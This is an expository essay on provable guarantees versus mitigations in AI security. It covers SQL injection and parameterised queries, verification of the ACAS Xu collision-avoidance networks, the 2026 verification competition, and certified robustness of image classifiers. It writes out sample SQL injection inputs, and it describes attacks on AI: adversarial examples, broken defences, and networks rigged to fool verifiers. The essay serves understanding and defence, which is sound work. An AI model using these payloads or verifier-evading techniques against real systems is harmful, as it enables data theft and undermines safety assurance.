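# Provable guarantees and mitigation in the security of deployed AI

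## Two aims: making attacks fail more often, and proving that they cannot succeed

The security of deployed AI concerns AI systems after release, when people who stand to gain from their errors can send them inputs they choose. These systems range from small neural networks that advise pilots to chatbots and agents. Agents are programs that let a language model act for a user by reading email, browsing the web or running code. A neural network is a mathematical function with many adjustable numbers, and training on examples sets those numbers. Because nobody writes down the network's rules, its developers cannot read through it for faults as they would with ordinary software.

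Defenders of deployed AI systems can try to make attacks fail more often or do less harm, or they can try to prove that no attack of a certain kind can succeed. A mitigation reduces how often attacks succeed or how much damage they do, without such a proof. A guarantee is a statement proved to hold for every attack in a stated class, under stated assumptions. Security professionals often call any countermeasure a mitigation, even one that removes a fault entirely. The narrower sense is more useful here because a buyer may be unable to tell a product that blocked every attack in last month's test from one that such attacks cannot defeat.

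Both aims need a threat model, which describes what the attacker can change, what he knows and what he wants. *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness* (Carlini, Athalye and colleagues, 2019) argues that without one, a claim of security is often either impossible to refute or trivially easy to refute. The paper advises assuming an adaptive attacker, meaning one who knows the defence and designs attacks against it. It argues that tests against anybody weaker have very little value, since a defender cannot count on keeping the design secret. A cryptographic key can stay secret, but its owner can replace it if it leaks, which is much harder to do with a whole defence.

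A proof also needs a specification, a precise statement of the property it is meant to establish. An example is "No text that a visitor types into this box can change the structure of the database command", which rules out one of the oldest problems in web security. "The website is secure" is too vague to serve as a specification.

### One query, handled both ways

SQL is the language in which most programs put questions to a database. In an SQL injection attack, a user types something that the database then executes as part of a command. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a non-profit organisation for software security, uses the example of a program that looks up an account balance by name. Suppose the program simply pastes the visitor's text between two quotation marks. A visitor who types `tom` produces this query:

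```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom'
```

A visitor who types `tom' or '1'='1` produces this one:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
```

The attacker's first quotation mark closes the name early, and the database treats the rest as a condition. Since '1' equals '1' for every row, the database returns every customer's balance.

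A developer might respond with a filter that rejects suspicious text. If the filter looks for `'1'='1`, the attacker can write `'2'='2` instead. If it deletes all quotation marks, it corrupts names like O'Brien and still fails to protect a query on an account number, where the attacker can enter `7 or 1=1`. A more careful developer "escapes" the input, marking special characters so that the database treats them as ordinary ones. OWASP strongly discourages relying on escaping, calls it frail, and does not guarantee that it stops every injection. All of these defenses are mitigations, which stop some attacks, perhaps most, but leave the attacker free to look for others that work.

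The parameterised query works differently. The developer writes the command first, with a placeholder where the name will go:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?
```

A parameterised query fixes the structure of the command before any user input arrives. The program then passes the input separately, as a value to compare with the names in the table. Given `tom' or '1'='1`, the database looks for a customer whose name is that entire string and finds none. No input can alter the command's structure, because the structure no longer depends on the input. This argument covers every possible string, so the developer does not have to anticipate or recognise particular attacks.

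Parameterised queries do not cover every case. A placeholder can stand for a value but not for the name of a table or column, so a developer who lets users choose a table has to check the choice against a list of permitted names. The technique also protects only the products that use it. In *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024), the US agencies CISA and the FBI point out that the database system MySQL has offered it since 2004. Yet they issued that alert after attackers had used SQL injection against a file-transfer product and affected thousands of organisations. David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, is more positive in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025). He writes that the flaw is now rare in websites, after a decade of breaches led to better defaults. Both accounts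 can be right, because good defaults protect even developers who never think about injection, but only in products built with those defaults.

### Three distinctions

Lowering the chance that an attack succeeds is different from limiting the damage when it does. The filter lowers the chance. To limit the damage, OWASP recommends giving each part of an application only the database permissions it needs. A login page, for example, needs to read the table of passwords but never to write to it. This kind of limit can carry its own guarantee, because even if an attacker gets an injection past the login page, the database will block any change to a password, however clever the injection was.

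A guarantee can concern the AI model itself or the software around it. Proving something about a model requires reasoning about what its thousands or billions of numbers do to every input in some range. To prove something about the surrounding software, we can assume the model might produce anything and show that certain outputs have no effect. For example, text from the model cannot send an email if the program has no function for sending email. David C recommends that designers of systems with language models concentrate on safeguards of this type, which constrain what the system can do, and rely less on keeping malicious text away from the model. These safeguards are a form of deterministic enforcement, in which ordinary software applies a rule and the outcome does not depend on a model's judgement. Such a guarantee does not cover the quality of the model's answers, so a model that cannot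 send email can still give its user a false summary of the inbox.

A proof that the property *P* holds for every input *x* in the set *D* is also different from a bound on probability, which has the form "the chance of failure is at most δ". In everyday engineering a small enough δ is often as good as a proof, but security is harder. Carlini and colleagues illustrate this with a system that fails one time in a billion. A million random tests have just under a 0.1% chance of exposing the fault, but an attacker does not test at random and can reuse the failing input once he finds it.

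Some bounds on probability hold against attackers, depending on where the randomness comes from. A bound holds if δ describes random numbers that the defender draws and the attacker cannot influence, as when software generates a secret key, because the attacker then gains nothing by choosing his input. It does not hold if δ describes the inputs of ordinary users, because an attacker can send something no ordinary user would send. *Robust Certificates for Neural Networks* (Delattre and Cao, 2025) similarly divides proofs about image classifiers into deterministic ones and ones that rest on the defender's own random sampling. *Pinky Promise or Ironclad* (Szyller, 2026), a lecture by a computer scientist at Aalto University, arranges security claims on a scale from "we tested it" through statements that hold with some probability to formal proof.

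### The four parts of a guarantee

Any guarantee has four parts: a property, a class of attacks, a set of assumptions and an object to which the proof applies. For the parameterised query, the property is that the command keeps the structure its developer wrote. The class of attacks is any text entered in the name box. The assumptions are that the database and its driver (the component that connects a program to it) keep values separate from commands, and that the attacker cannot rewrite the program. The object is this query, as it runs in this application. A correct proof can still fail to protect anyone if one of these parts does not match the deployment.

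The guarantee covers only injection. An attacker who types another customer's real name into the box leaves the command's structure intact and may still see that customer's balance. OWASP warns that attackers can swap one legal value for another that they have no right to use, so the bank also needs to check who is asking.

A proof may cover too narrow a class of attacks. Many proofs about image classifiers cover small changes to the pixels, and Szyller points out that they do not cover a rotation or a shift in colour. Carlini and colleagues hold that such an attack does not break the defence, because it was never claimed to resist it. That is a fair rule for judging research, but it is less reassuring to the operator of a working system, because attackers are not limited to the changes the proof covers.

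An assumption can fail in a setting that few people check. NIST's *CVE-2024-1597*, an entry in the US government's catalogue of software flaws, describes a PostgreSQL database driver that let attackers inject commands despite parameterised queries. The flaw appeared only in a non-default mode, in which the driver itself wrote the values into the command. It also required a placeholder for a number immediately after a minus sign, with a placeholder for text later on the same line. The reasoning behind parameterised queries was still sound, but it depends on values being kept separate from commands, and the driver failed to do that.

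The least obvious mismatch is between the network in the proof and the network that runs. A proof normally treats a neural network as a function on exact real numbers, but a computer rounds at every step, so even the order of an addition matters. In common double-precision arithmetic, 2⁵³ + 1 − 2⁵³ comes to 0, and 2⁵³ − 2⁵³ + 1 comes to 1. In *No Soundness in the Real World*, Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity (2025) used this to attack verifiers, the programs that try to prove that a network meets a specification. They built networks that detect the order or precision of the arithmetic and change their behaviour accordingly. These networks were harmless in exact arithmetic but harmful on particular machines, and every verifier they tested missed the difference. Someone has to plant the behaviour in the network beforehand, so the attack matters most to people who get their models from suppliers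 they do not trust. But the gap between proof and deployment exists for any network that is verified in exact arithmetic and run with rounding.

### How researchers came to want proofs

Researchers had shown how to fool spam filters by 2004, according to a survey by NIST (2025), the US standards institute. The subject grew because of a discovery reported in *Intriguing properties of neural networks* (2013). Szegedy, Zaremba and colleagues took images that a network classified correctly and searched for the smallest change that would make it misclassify them. They found one for every image they tried, usually too slight for a person to notice, and called the altered images adversarial examples. One well-known network classified a whole row of unrelated pictures as ostriches after they were altered. Random noise that left handwritten digits hardly readable still let a network classify about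 half of them correctly, but far smaller changes found by search reduced its accuracy to zero. Many of the altered images also fooled networks trained on different data, so the weakness was not limited to one model. *Most Convolutional Networks Suffer from Small Adversarial Perturbations* (2026) treats this weakness as normal for a common type of image network, as its title indicates.

Defences followed quickly, but most were broken. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (Athalye, Carlini and Wagner, 2018) examined nine that had appeared at a leading conference that year, leaving aside two papers that offered proofs. Seven of the nine hid the gradient, which an attacker uses to work out how to change each pixel, but did not remove the adversarial examples themselves. The researchers approximated or recovered the gradient and defeated six of the seven completely and the other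 in part. Designers then began testing their defences against adaptive attackers, but *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses* (Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues, 2020) got past thirteen more, almost all of which had come through such tests. The pattern has repeated with language models. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) bypassed twelve recent defences, most of them in over 90% of attempts. Delattre and Cao call this a cat-and-mouse game and give it as the reason to look for proofs. NIST lists three approaches that have held up: training on adversarial examples, averaging a network's answers over random noise, and formal verification. Only the last two yield proofs, and all three reduce accuracy, require more computation, or both.

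### The case for each aim

The argument for guarantees is that an attacker has to find only one way through, while a defender, as Athalye and colleagues put it, must show that no attack can succeed. Tests cannot show that. Szyller objects that a defender who relies on them assumes that the tester is the best attacker there is, when "tomorrow's attacker is already better". The thirteen defences of 2020 support his objection, since most of their designers had tried to break their own work and had stopped too early. A low failure rate can also mislead if an attacker can easily make many attempts. If each attempt succeeds 1% of the time, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of a hundred succeeds is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. A proof whose four parts match the deployment holds however many attempts are made, and it also covers attacks that nobody has invented yet.

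Those who favour mitigation can reply that nobody knows how to specify most of what people want from AI. No formula, for example, identifies the chemistry questions whose answers would help a poisoner. Even where a formula exists, the proof may cover very little. In 2019 Carlini and colleagues judged that the best defences without proofs often gave orders of magnitude more robustness than the provable ones. That was an estimate, and estimates of this kind have often been wrong. Still, Szyller, who wants more guarantees, conceded in 2026 that proofs for any complex model still cover only tiny changes, and that formal verification scales poorly.

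The 63% figure also leaves out constraints on attackers. David C expects that they will usually have to refine an attack over several tries, and that a defender who logs failed actions may catch them. If monitoring cuts an attacker off after ten attempts, the 63% falls to about 10%. He doubts that language models will ever have a remedy as complete as the parameterised query, because they receive instructions and data as a single stream of text. He recommends that defenders work to reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks instead, and suggests that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be the wrong place for a language model.

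## Aircraft collision avoidance: proofs about small neural networks

A standard test case for neural network verification comes from ACAS Xu, a collision avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. When another aircraft, the intruder, comes near, the system advises whether to turn and in which direction. Its designers worked out the best advice for each kind of encounter in advance and stored it in a table of more than two gigabytes. That is a lot of memory for a computer certified for use on board, so researchers trained neural networks that imitate the table and take up less than three megabytes.

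The system uses 45 networks, one for each combination of the previous advice (five options) and the time left until the two aircraft reach the same height (nine values). Each network takes in five numbers: the distance to the intruder, the direction to it, its heading relative to the aircraft's own, and the speeds of both. It returns five scores, for "clear of conflict", a weak or strong left turn, and a weak or strong right turn. The system gives the advice with the lowest score. Each network has six layers of 50 units between input and output. Each unit takes a weighted sum of the previous layer's values, adds a constant, then applies ReLU(z) = max(0, z), which keeps positive numbers and turns negative ones into zero. The weights and constants total about 13,000 parameters per network.

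### A property that fits on a few lines

Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017), in *Reluplex*, wrote down ten properties that these networks ought to have. One of them says that if an intruder is straight ahead and flying towards the aircraft, the network never answers "clear of conflict". In numbers it reads:

```
if    1500 ≤ distance ≤ 1800          (feet)
and   -0.06 ≤ direction ≤ 0.06        (radians; 0 is straight ahead)
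and   relative heading ≥ 3.10         (radians; 3.14 is head-on)
and   own speed ≥ 980, intruder's speed ≥ 960   (feet per second)
then  "clear of conflict" does not have the lowest score
```

An engineer can write this property down because every input is a physical measurement with a unit. "Straight ahead" becomes a range of angles, and the output is one of five pieces of advice, one of which is plainly wrong in this situation. For image classifiers, nobody has a formula that distinguishes pictures of aircraft from other pictures by their pixel values, so researchers who certify the classifiers' accuracy prove a different kind of property.

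The head-on property is also rather modest. Two aircraft approaching each other at 1,940 feet per second or more cover 1,800 feet in less than a second, and a strong turn changes the heading by only three degrees in that time. So a proof of the property shows that the network gives a sensible answer in one region of its inputs, but not that the answer comes early enough to prevent a collision.

### The first verification and its worst case

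Before 2017, dedicated verifiers could handle networks with perhaps 20 units in a single layer. Katz and colleagues handled 300 units by extending the simplex method, a standard algorithm for solving systems of linear equations and inequalities. Their program, Reluplex, looks for a counterexample, an input in the stated range whose output breaks the property. If it rules out every candidate, the property holds. Because ReLU is not linear, Reluplex lets a unit's value break the ReLU rule temporarily, then repairs it. Only after five repairs to the same unit does the program split the problem into two cases, one with the unit switched on (passing its input through) and one with it switched off (giving zero).

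The head-on property held on all 42 networks the team checked, and the proofs took just under eight hours in total. Proving a property about distant, slow intruders took four and a half days for 41 networks, and Reluplex ran out of time on four more. It also ran out of time on the property that a network never advises a strong turn while the aircraft are far apart in height. One search produced an input for which a network's advice differed from the table's, and the team planned to correct this by retraining. Another search found violations in 35 of 36 networks, but here the specification needed correcting more than the networks did. The team decided the violations were acceptable because the networks tend to repeat their previous advice, so they may keep advising a turn when the intruder is already far away.

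The same paper proves that the verification problem is NP-complete. For problems of this type, anyone can check a proposed solution quickly, but nobody knows a method that finds one quickly in every case. Checking is easy here, since one only has to run the network on the proposed counterexample. To show that finding one is hard, Katz and colleagues translated a famous hard problem, 3-SAT, into networks. A 3-SAT puzzle is a list of clauses such as "A or B or not C", and the task is to make all of them true at once. Write 1 for true and 0 for false, and let q₁, q₂ and q₃ be the three parts of a clause. Then

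1 − ReLU(1 − (q₁ + q₂ + q₃))

equals 1 if at least one part is true and 0 if none is. A network can compute this for each of *n* clauses and add up the results, with a few extra units to keep the inputs close to 0 or 1. Its output can reach *n* only if the puzzle has a solution. A verifier that was fast on every network would therefore be fast on every 3-SAT puzzle, and no such program is known.

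This result concerns the worst case and doesn't establish how hard it is to verify the networks people train in practice. A network with 300 units has up to 2³⁰⁰ combinations of on and off, a number with 91 digits, but Reluplex needed 52,080 splits to check the head-on property across all 42 networks.

### Whether the networks ever flew

These 45 networks appear to have remained a research testbed. Marston's *ACAS-Xu Initial Self-Separation Flight Tests* describes flights with ACAS Xu in November and December 2014, before the 2016 proposal to replace the table with a network. Katz and colleagues call the networks an early prototype. The agenda for a September 2020 meeting of RTCA, the American body that writes standards for aviation electronics, included approval of the ACAS Xu standard but no item on neural networks (RTCA, 2021). By 2026, the manual for a commercial MathWorks product included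 the networks in a worked example, *Verify VNN-COMP Benchmark for ACAS Xu Neural Networks Using α,β-CROWN*.

One source, the International Federation of Airworthiness, writes however that modern implementations of ACAS X, the wider family of systems, use deep neural networks to compress the table. If this is right, some aircraft may carry networks related to the 45 that researchers have verified, but the statement does not identify those 45 as the ones in use.

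### How a verifier reaches a proof

A network with two units is enough to show the method. Let *x* lie between −1 and 1, and let

y = ReLU(x) + ReLU(−x).

Suppose we want to prove that *y* is at most 1.5. The simplest approach, interval bounds, computes a lowest and highest value for each unit, layer by layer. ReLU(x) and ReLU(−x) each lie between 0 and 1, so this method bounds *y* between 0 and 2. That bound is correct but too loose to prove the property, because it allows both units to reach 1 at once, which would require *x* to be both 1 and −1.

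Splitting the range at *x* = 0 solves the problem. If *x* is 0 or more, the second unit gives 0 and *y* = *x*, which is at most 1. If *x* is 0 or less, the first unit gives 0 and *y* = −*x*, which is also at most 1. The two halves cover every input, so *y* never exceeds 1 and the property holds. However, each undecided unit, one that could be on or off within the range, may double the number of cases, so *n* undecided units can lead to 2ⁿ cases.

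Modern verifiers avoid most of these splits by using straight lines as bounds in place of fixed numbers. If a unit's input *z* lies between a negative number *l* and a positive number *u*, then

αz ≤ ReLU(z) ≤ u(z − l)/(u − l),

where α can be any number from 0 to 1. In the example, the upper lines are (1 + x)/2 for the first unit and (1 − x)/2 for the second. When we add them, *x* cancels and the sum is exactly 1. The lines preserve the fact that both units depend on the same *x*, so they prove the property without any split. Applied layer by layer, this technique is known as linear bound propagation.

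Lines are sometimes too loose to prove a true bound. For example, *y* = ReLU(*x* + 0.5) − ReLU(*x*) has a maximum of 0.5 on the same range, but the best upper bound that these lines can give is 0.75, which is too high to prove that *y* stays below 0.6. Splitting the range at *x* = 0 makes the proof possible. On the right half, both units are on and *y* is exactly 0.5. On the left half, the second unit is off, and the upper line for the first is (1 + *x*)/2, which is at most 0.5 there.

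Branch and bound combines the two ideas. The verifier computes linear bounds for the whole range and stops if they prove the property. Otherwise it picks an undecided unit, splits the problem into an "on" case and an "off" case, and computes new bounds for each. It drops every case it has proved and splits the others again, until none is left or it finds a counterexample. Each split also tightens the bounds on later units, often enough to show whether they are on or off. Katz and colleagues had already noticed that splitting on about a tenth of the units often decided all the rest. Much of the progress since then has come from choosing the slopes α well and from running many cases at once on graphics processors.

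### The 2026 competition

Developers of verifiers compare their programs in a yearly contest. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen et al., 2026) describes the latest round, whose results the organisers presented in Lisbon in July. Each task consists of a network, a property and a time limit. The organisers ran all 13 tools on rented machines of equal cost. A tool earned 10 points for a correct proof or a valid counterexample, lost 150 for an incorrect answer, and lost none for running out of time. On each benchmark, or set of related tasks, the organisers scaled the points so that the best tool received 100. The main track had 24 benchmarks, so the maximum score was 2,400.

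α,β-CROWN, from a team led at the University of Illinois, won with 2,344.0. Vibecheck, from Stony Brook University, followed closely with 2,278.6, well ahead of the French tool PyRAT (1,813.6) and NeuralSAT from George Mason University (1,725.5). The winner solved 3,164 of the 3,373 tasks, or 94%, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. That percentage flatters the field somewhat, because almost a third of the tasks concern sentence classifiers with only about 4,000 parameters. A score of 100 does not mean that a tool solved everything, either. On one set of image classifiers α,β-CROWN received full marks for 160 tasks out of 200.

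The ACAS Xu networks are no longer hard for the best tools. The competition tested four of the ten original properties on all 45 networks and the other six on one network each, for a total of 186 tasks with a limit of 116 seconds each. α,β-CROWN, Vibecheck and PyRAT solved all of them, finding that the property held in 139 tasks and failed in 47. In 2017, checking the property about distant, slow intruders took an average of 2.7 hours per network. Faster hardware accounts for some of the difference.

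Doug Wehbe and Stanley Bak built Vibecheck over two months with Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. They describe it as "vibe-coded", meaning that the AI wrote the code at their direction. Vibecheck combines several known techniques with a new solver for the branching step. It overtook tools that research groups had developed over years, though Bak is a specialist who also helped to write the competition report and proposed some of its benchmarks.

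### Why size alone does not measure difficulty

How hard a network is to verify depends on more than its number of parameters. The largest network in the competition has 138 million parameters and classifies photographs. Another benchmark uses vision transformers, which apply the architecture behind language models to images. These networks had to be cut down to two or three layers and about 70,000 parameters, and they classify only about 60% of ordinary test images correctly.

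The number of undecided units affects the difficulty of verification more than the size of the network does. If an attacker may change only one pixel slightly, most units in even a huge network stay on or stay off for every allowed change, and the verifier can treat them as linear. Some tasks on the 138-million-parameter network allow only such a one-pixel change, while others allow changes to all 150,528 input values. The difficulty also depends on the type of calculation. A ReLU unit becomes exactly linear once the verifier has decided whether it is on or off. Transformers also contain a function called softmax, which remains curved however many times the verifier splits its range, so the bounds stay somewhat loose.

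Results from four of the benchmarks show how little the parameter count predicts:

| Networks | Parameters | Inputs | Solved by the best tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 5 | 186 of 186 |
| Image generators for road scenes | 500,000 to 68 million | 5 | 20 of 21 |
| Fully connected image classifiers | 575,000 to 1.1 million | 784 or 3,072 | 152 of 180 |
| Image classifiers with 100 classes | 2.5 to 3.8 million | 3,072 | 160 of 200 |

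The comparison is rough, because time limits differ and the last benchmark's proposers had removed the easiest tasks. A benchmark called Relusplitter allows a cleaner comparison. It rewrites a network to compute the same function with more undecided units. This doesn't change whether the property holds, but it makes the property harder to verify.

### Wrong answers from verifiers

Verifiers are complicated programs and can have bugs. Eight of the 13 tools returned answers that the organisers counted as incorrect or that lacked a valid counterexample. Agate, an early prototype, had 955, which its developer attributes to a last-minute bug that spoiled its counterexamples. NeuralSAT had 94, nnenum 58, SuperSimple 14, ACT 10 and SobolBox 2, while CORA and the winner, α,β-CROWN, had one each. Vibecheck had none. These counts mix different kinds of failure. A tool that correctly reports a violation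 but gives an invalid counterexample does little harm, but a false proof is much worse because someone may rely on it. SobolBox can produce false proofs by design, because it samples a network's outputs and reports that a property holds if the samples give no sign of a violation.

False proofs are also the hardest errors to notice. For most tasks the organisers do not know the right answer, so they can reject a proof only if another tool finds a counterexample. If no tool finds one, the false proof earns 10 points. Two benchmarks try to catch such proofs. One consists of 3-SAT puzzles with known answers, translated into networks much as in the proof of NP-completeness. The other hides counterexamples where the usual attacks are unlikely to find them. A more thorough remedy, which Ladner and colleagues name as a long-term goal, is to require each verifier to output a proof that a separate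 program can check. Users would then have to trust only the checker, whether a person or an AI agent had written the verifier.

Because of rounding, a counterexample that only just violates a property on one computer may satisfy it on another, which can make it unclear which answer is right. In 2026 the organisers ran each proposed counterexample in one fixed software environment. If it fell short of violating the property by no more than 0.0001, they did not penalise the tool that proposed it, but did not let the example overturn another tool's proof.

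### What the proof leaves out

The same problem affects the aircraft proofs. Reluplex used rounded arithmetic because exact arithmetic is at least ten times slower. Katz and colleagues acknowledge that their checks on the accumulated error do not guarantee a correct result, so the first proofs about ACAS Xu came with a small reservation. PyRAT's developers say that it accounts for rounding when it runs on an ordinary processor. A further step is to verify the program that will actually run, rather than the idealised network. *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (2025) supplies 912 test programs in C for this purpose, ranging from single units to whole networks, with answers known in advance. Verifying the program addresses the gap that Szász and colleagues exploited, but it does not help if the network's inputs are wrong.

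The proofs take the five inputs as given, so an attacker who can falsify the aircraft's sensor data does not need to find a flaw in the network. Another of the ten properties requires the network to answer "clear of conflict" if the intruder is far away, well off to one side and heading in the opposite direction. Reluplex proved this property for the network concerned. If false data place a nearby intruder in that position, the proved property guarantees that the network will answer "clear of conflict", which is the wrong advice for the real situation.

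Even with perfect sensors, a series of individually reasonable answers may end in a collision, because the system gives new advice every second and each turn changes the next set of inputs. Bak and Tran (2022), in *Neural Network Compression of ACAS Xu Early Prototype is Unsafe*, therefore examined the whole loop of network and aircraft. They began with every near-collision, defined as two aircraft at the same height and less than 500 feet apart. They then worked backwards one second at a time, checking which earlier positions could have led there and whether the networks would have given the advice required. To keep the number of cases finite, they rounded positions, speeds and headings to a grid, so that each check only required running a network. A chain of steps that reached back to a distance of more than 60,760 feet, where the system is not yet active, was a route from a safe start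 to a near-collision.

Bak and Tran assumed that sensors were perfect, the aircraft followed all advice immediately, and the intruder flew in a straight line at constant speed. Even under these favorable assumptions, they found encounters that ended in near-collisions, and these also occurred with the original networks, without the rounding. When they restricted the aircraft's own speed to a narrower range, they could prove that the rounded version was safe. So the grid method can produce a guarantee about collisions themselves, though here it required the narrower speed range. The method works because the system has so few inputs. A grid over the thousands of pixels in an image would have far too many points to check.

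### What regulators accept as evidence

Europe is still developing its rules for machine learning in aircraft. EASA, the European Union's aviation safety agency, published its first regulatory proposal on AI in November 2025. According to Aviacionaldia's *EASA publishes its first regulatory proposal on artificial intelligence in aviation* (2025), the proposal prepares the industry for AI that assists people and AI that works in a team with them. It seems to leave out a drone that makes its own turns without human involvement. Unmanned Airspace reports that the proposal offers technical guidance in line with the EU AI Act's requirements for high-risk systems, and that EASA opened it to public comment for three months. The agency planned a second proposal for 2026 to apply this general framework to particular areas of aviation.

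In a 2026 paper on its approach, EASA asks for evidence that a system performs its intended function safely and reliably within a declared range of operating conditions. The evidence includes defined requirements, verification, robustness testing, performance monitoring, control of changes to the system, and a link to the aircraft's safety assessment. Developers must also show that they selected and labelled their data properly. A proof about a network can supply part of the verification but cannot replace the other items, several of which concern matters that the proofs about ACAS Xu leave out.

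Manzanas Lopez, Johnson and colleagues (2023), in *Evaluation of Neural Network Verification Methods for Air-to-Air Collision Avoidance*, hold that networks of this kind cannot be certified for aircraft unless someone has exhaustively verified that they are safe. Katz and colleagues noted that earlier certification work on collision avoidance had relied on 1.5 million simulated encounters, and that a network can still fail at a point between the simulated ones.

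Industry has begun with functions where errors are less dangerous. The aerospace company Collins contributed networks with between 60,000 and 262,000 parameters to the competition. These networks estimate how much longer an aircraft component will last. The properties to be proved require, among other things, that the estimate stays within an expected range when the sensor readings do. Seven tools solved all 62 tasks in 2026. A wrong estimate could still lead an airline to replace a part too late, but maintenance staff can inspect the part before the next flight. An aircraft that receives bad collision advice may have only seconds to recover.

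## Image classifiers: proofs that small changes do not matter

Without a formula for what an image shows, researchers who want proofs about image classifiers settle for a weaker property than those of the aircraft networks. They take one image and prove that the network gives the same label to every slightly altered version of it. For a network *F*, an image *x* and a radius ε, the property is

F(x′) = F(x) for every x′ with ‖x′ − x‖ ≤ ε,

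where ‖x′ − x‖ is the size of the change. A proof of this property for one image is a certificate.

The property does not require the label to be correct. A network that labels a dog as a cat, and does the same for all nearby images, satisfies it. Researchers therefore report certified accuracy, the share of test images that a network labels correctly and provably keeps labelling the same way under every change up to a stated size. If this share is 40%, no attack that alters the test images within that size can push the network's accuracy on them below 40%. The accuracy measured under known attacks, by contrast, is only an upper limit on the true robustness, because a stronger attack may lower it, as Mangal, Leino and colleagues point out in *Is Certifying ℓp Robustness Still Worthwhile?* (2023).

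### The size of a change

A colour image has three values per pixel, for red, green and blue. On a scale from 0 to 1, each value usually changes in steps of 1/255. Researchers mostly measure a change to an image either by its Euclidean size, which is the square root of the sum of all the squared changes, or by the largest change to any single value.

In the Euclidean measure, moving one colour channel of one pixel from 0 to 1 is a change of size 1. Turning one black pixel white changes all three of its channels, so the size is √3, or about 1.73. Within a radius of 36/255, which is common in this research, an attacker can move a single value by up to 36 of 255 steps if the rest of the image stays the same.

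An attacker can also spread the change thinly across the image. In an image of 224 by 224 pixels, which has 150,528 values, an evenly spread change of size 1 alters each value by about two-thirds of a step. Brightening the whole image by one step is a change of size 1.52, so a certificate of radius 1 does not cover it, although hardly anyone would notice it.

### Dividing the margin by the slope

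One kind of certificate relies on a limit to how fast a network's output can change. Let *f(x)* be the margin, the gap between the score of the winning label and that of a rival. The margin has Lipschitz constant *K* if it changes at most *K* times as fast as the input:

|f(x) − f(x′)| ≤ K‖x − x′‖.

The classifier can switch to the rival label only if the margin falls to zero. With a margin of 0.3 and *K* = 1, an attacker has to change the image by at least 0.3 to cause this. In general, the safe radius is the margin divided by *K*, and with many labels the certifier takes the smallest radius over all rivals. The check takes one run of the network, because *K* is the same for every image and the developer can compute it in advance.

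Finding a value of *K* small enough to be useful is much harder. The standard rule multiplies the constants of all the layers, and the result can be far too high. For example, if one layer doubles one coordinate and halves another, and the next layer does the reverse, each layer alone can double a distance, so the rule gives *K* = 4. But together the layers return every input unchanged, so the true value is 1, and the rule makes the certified radius four times too small. The error compounds with depth. If the rule overstated the effect of each of 32 layers by 10%, the radius would shrink by a factor of 21.

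Designers avoid the problem by using layers that preserve distances exactly, as rotations and reflections do. The matrices for these operations are called orthogonal, and any chain of them has *K* = 1. But an ordinary training step leaves a matrix slightly non-orthogonal. Earlier methods corrected this with calculations that took a lot of compute, and most of the resulting networks had fewer than about 32 million parameters.

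Hu, Hu and Fredrikson (2026), in *LipNeXt*, made the training steps themselves into small rotations. If *X* is orthogonal and *A* satisfies Aᵀ = −A, then *X* exp(*A*) is orthogonal too, where

exp(A) = I + A + A²/2 + A³/6 + …

Because each step is small, the first few terms are usually enough. After every pass through the training data, the program removes the error that has built up.

The network must also combine neighbouring pixels. Most image networks do this with convolutions, which take weighted sums over small patches. Hu and colleagues prove that a convolution on a single channel, with edges that wrap around, preserves all distances only if it has exactly one nonzero weight, equal to 1 or −1. Such a convolution only shifts the image and, if the weight is −1, reverses its sign. LipNeXt therefore shifts some of its channels by one pixel in each of four directions and mixes the channels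 with orthogonal matrices. Its nonlinear step takes the absolute value of part of the channels, which never moves two numbers further apart.

### LipNeXt on ImageNet

Hu and colleagues trained two 2-billion-parameter versions of LipNeXt on ImageNet, a large collection of photographs used as a standard test for classifiers. The version for radius 36/255 labelled 57.0% of test images correctly and had a certified accuracy of 41.2%. The version for radius 1 labelled 41.0% correctly and had a certified accuracy of 22.4%.

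The improvement is clear at radius 1, where the earlier Lipschitz network in the comparison had a certified accuracy of 14.2%. At the smaller radius, the improvement depends on which result LipNeXt is compared with. BRONet, a network with 86 million parameters, reached 37.6%, or 40.7% with extra generated training images. LipNeXt used no extra images on ImageNet, but it needed more than twenty times as many parameters to beat BRONet's better result by half a point. Doubling LipNeXt from 1 to 2 billion parameters added only 0.9 points at the smaller radius and 1.3 at the larger.

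Chance may account for part of such gains. In *On the Extreme Variance of Certified Local Robustness Across Model Seeds*, Le and Cao (2026) trained ten small networks on handwritten digits, changing only the seed, the number that fixes the random choices in training. All ten were about 99.5% accurate, but at one radius the share of 100 test images with a proof averaged 54.3%, with a standard deviation of 28.9 percentage points across the networks. Le and Cao compared this with 11 papers on certified robustness, including the one on LipNeXt, and found that none reported confidence intervals or claimed a gain of ten percentage points or more.

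The comparison is unfair to LipNeXt because the digit networks had ordinary training, with nothing to keep their outputs from changing quickly, while LipNeXt has *K* = 1 whatever the seed. Its results may vary far less, but checking this would take several training runs. The variation matters most for claims that one training method beats another. A certificate for a particular network and image remains valid regardless of the seed.

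### Voting over noisy copies

Randomized smoothing produces certificates for almost any classifier, because it changes only the steps before and after the classifier runs. It makes many copies of an image and adds random noise to every colour value in each copy. It then runs the classifier on all the copies and returns the most frequent label.

Let σ be the standard deviation of the noise. Let *p*₁ be a lower bound on the probability that a noisy copy gets the top label, and *p*₂ an upper bound for the runner-up. Cullen, Montague and colleagues (2025), in *Position*, a paper otherwise critical of certificates, give the safe Euclidean radius as

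r = (σ/2) × (Φ⁻¹(p₁) − Φ⁻¹(p₂)).

Φ⁻¹(*p*) is the value below which a standard normal variable falls with probability *p*. With σ = 0.5, *p*₁ = 0.9 and *p*₂ = 0.1, Φ⁻¹(*p*₁) is about 1.28, Φ⁻¹(*p*₂) is about −1.28, and the radius is about 0.64.

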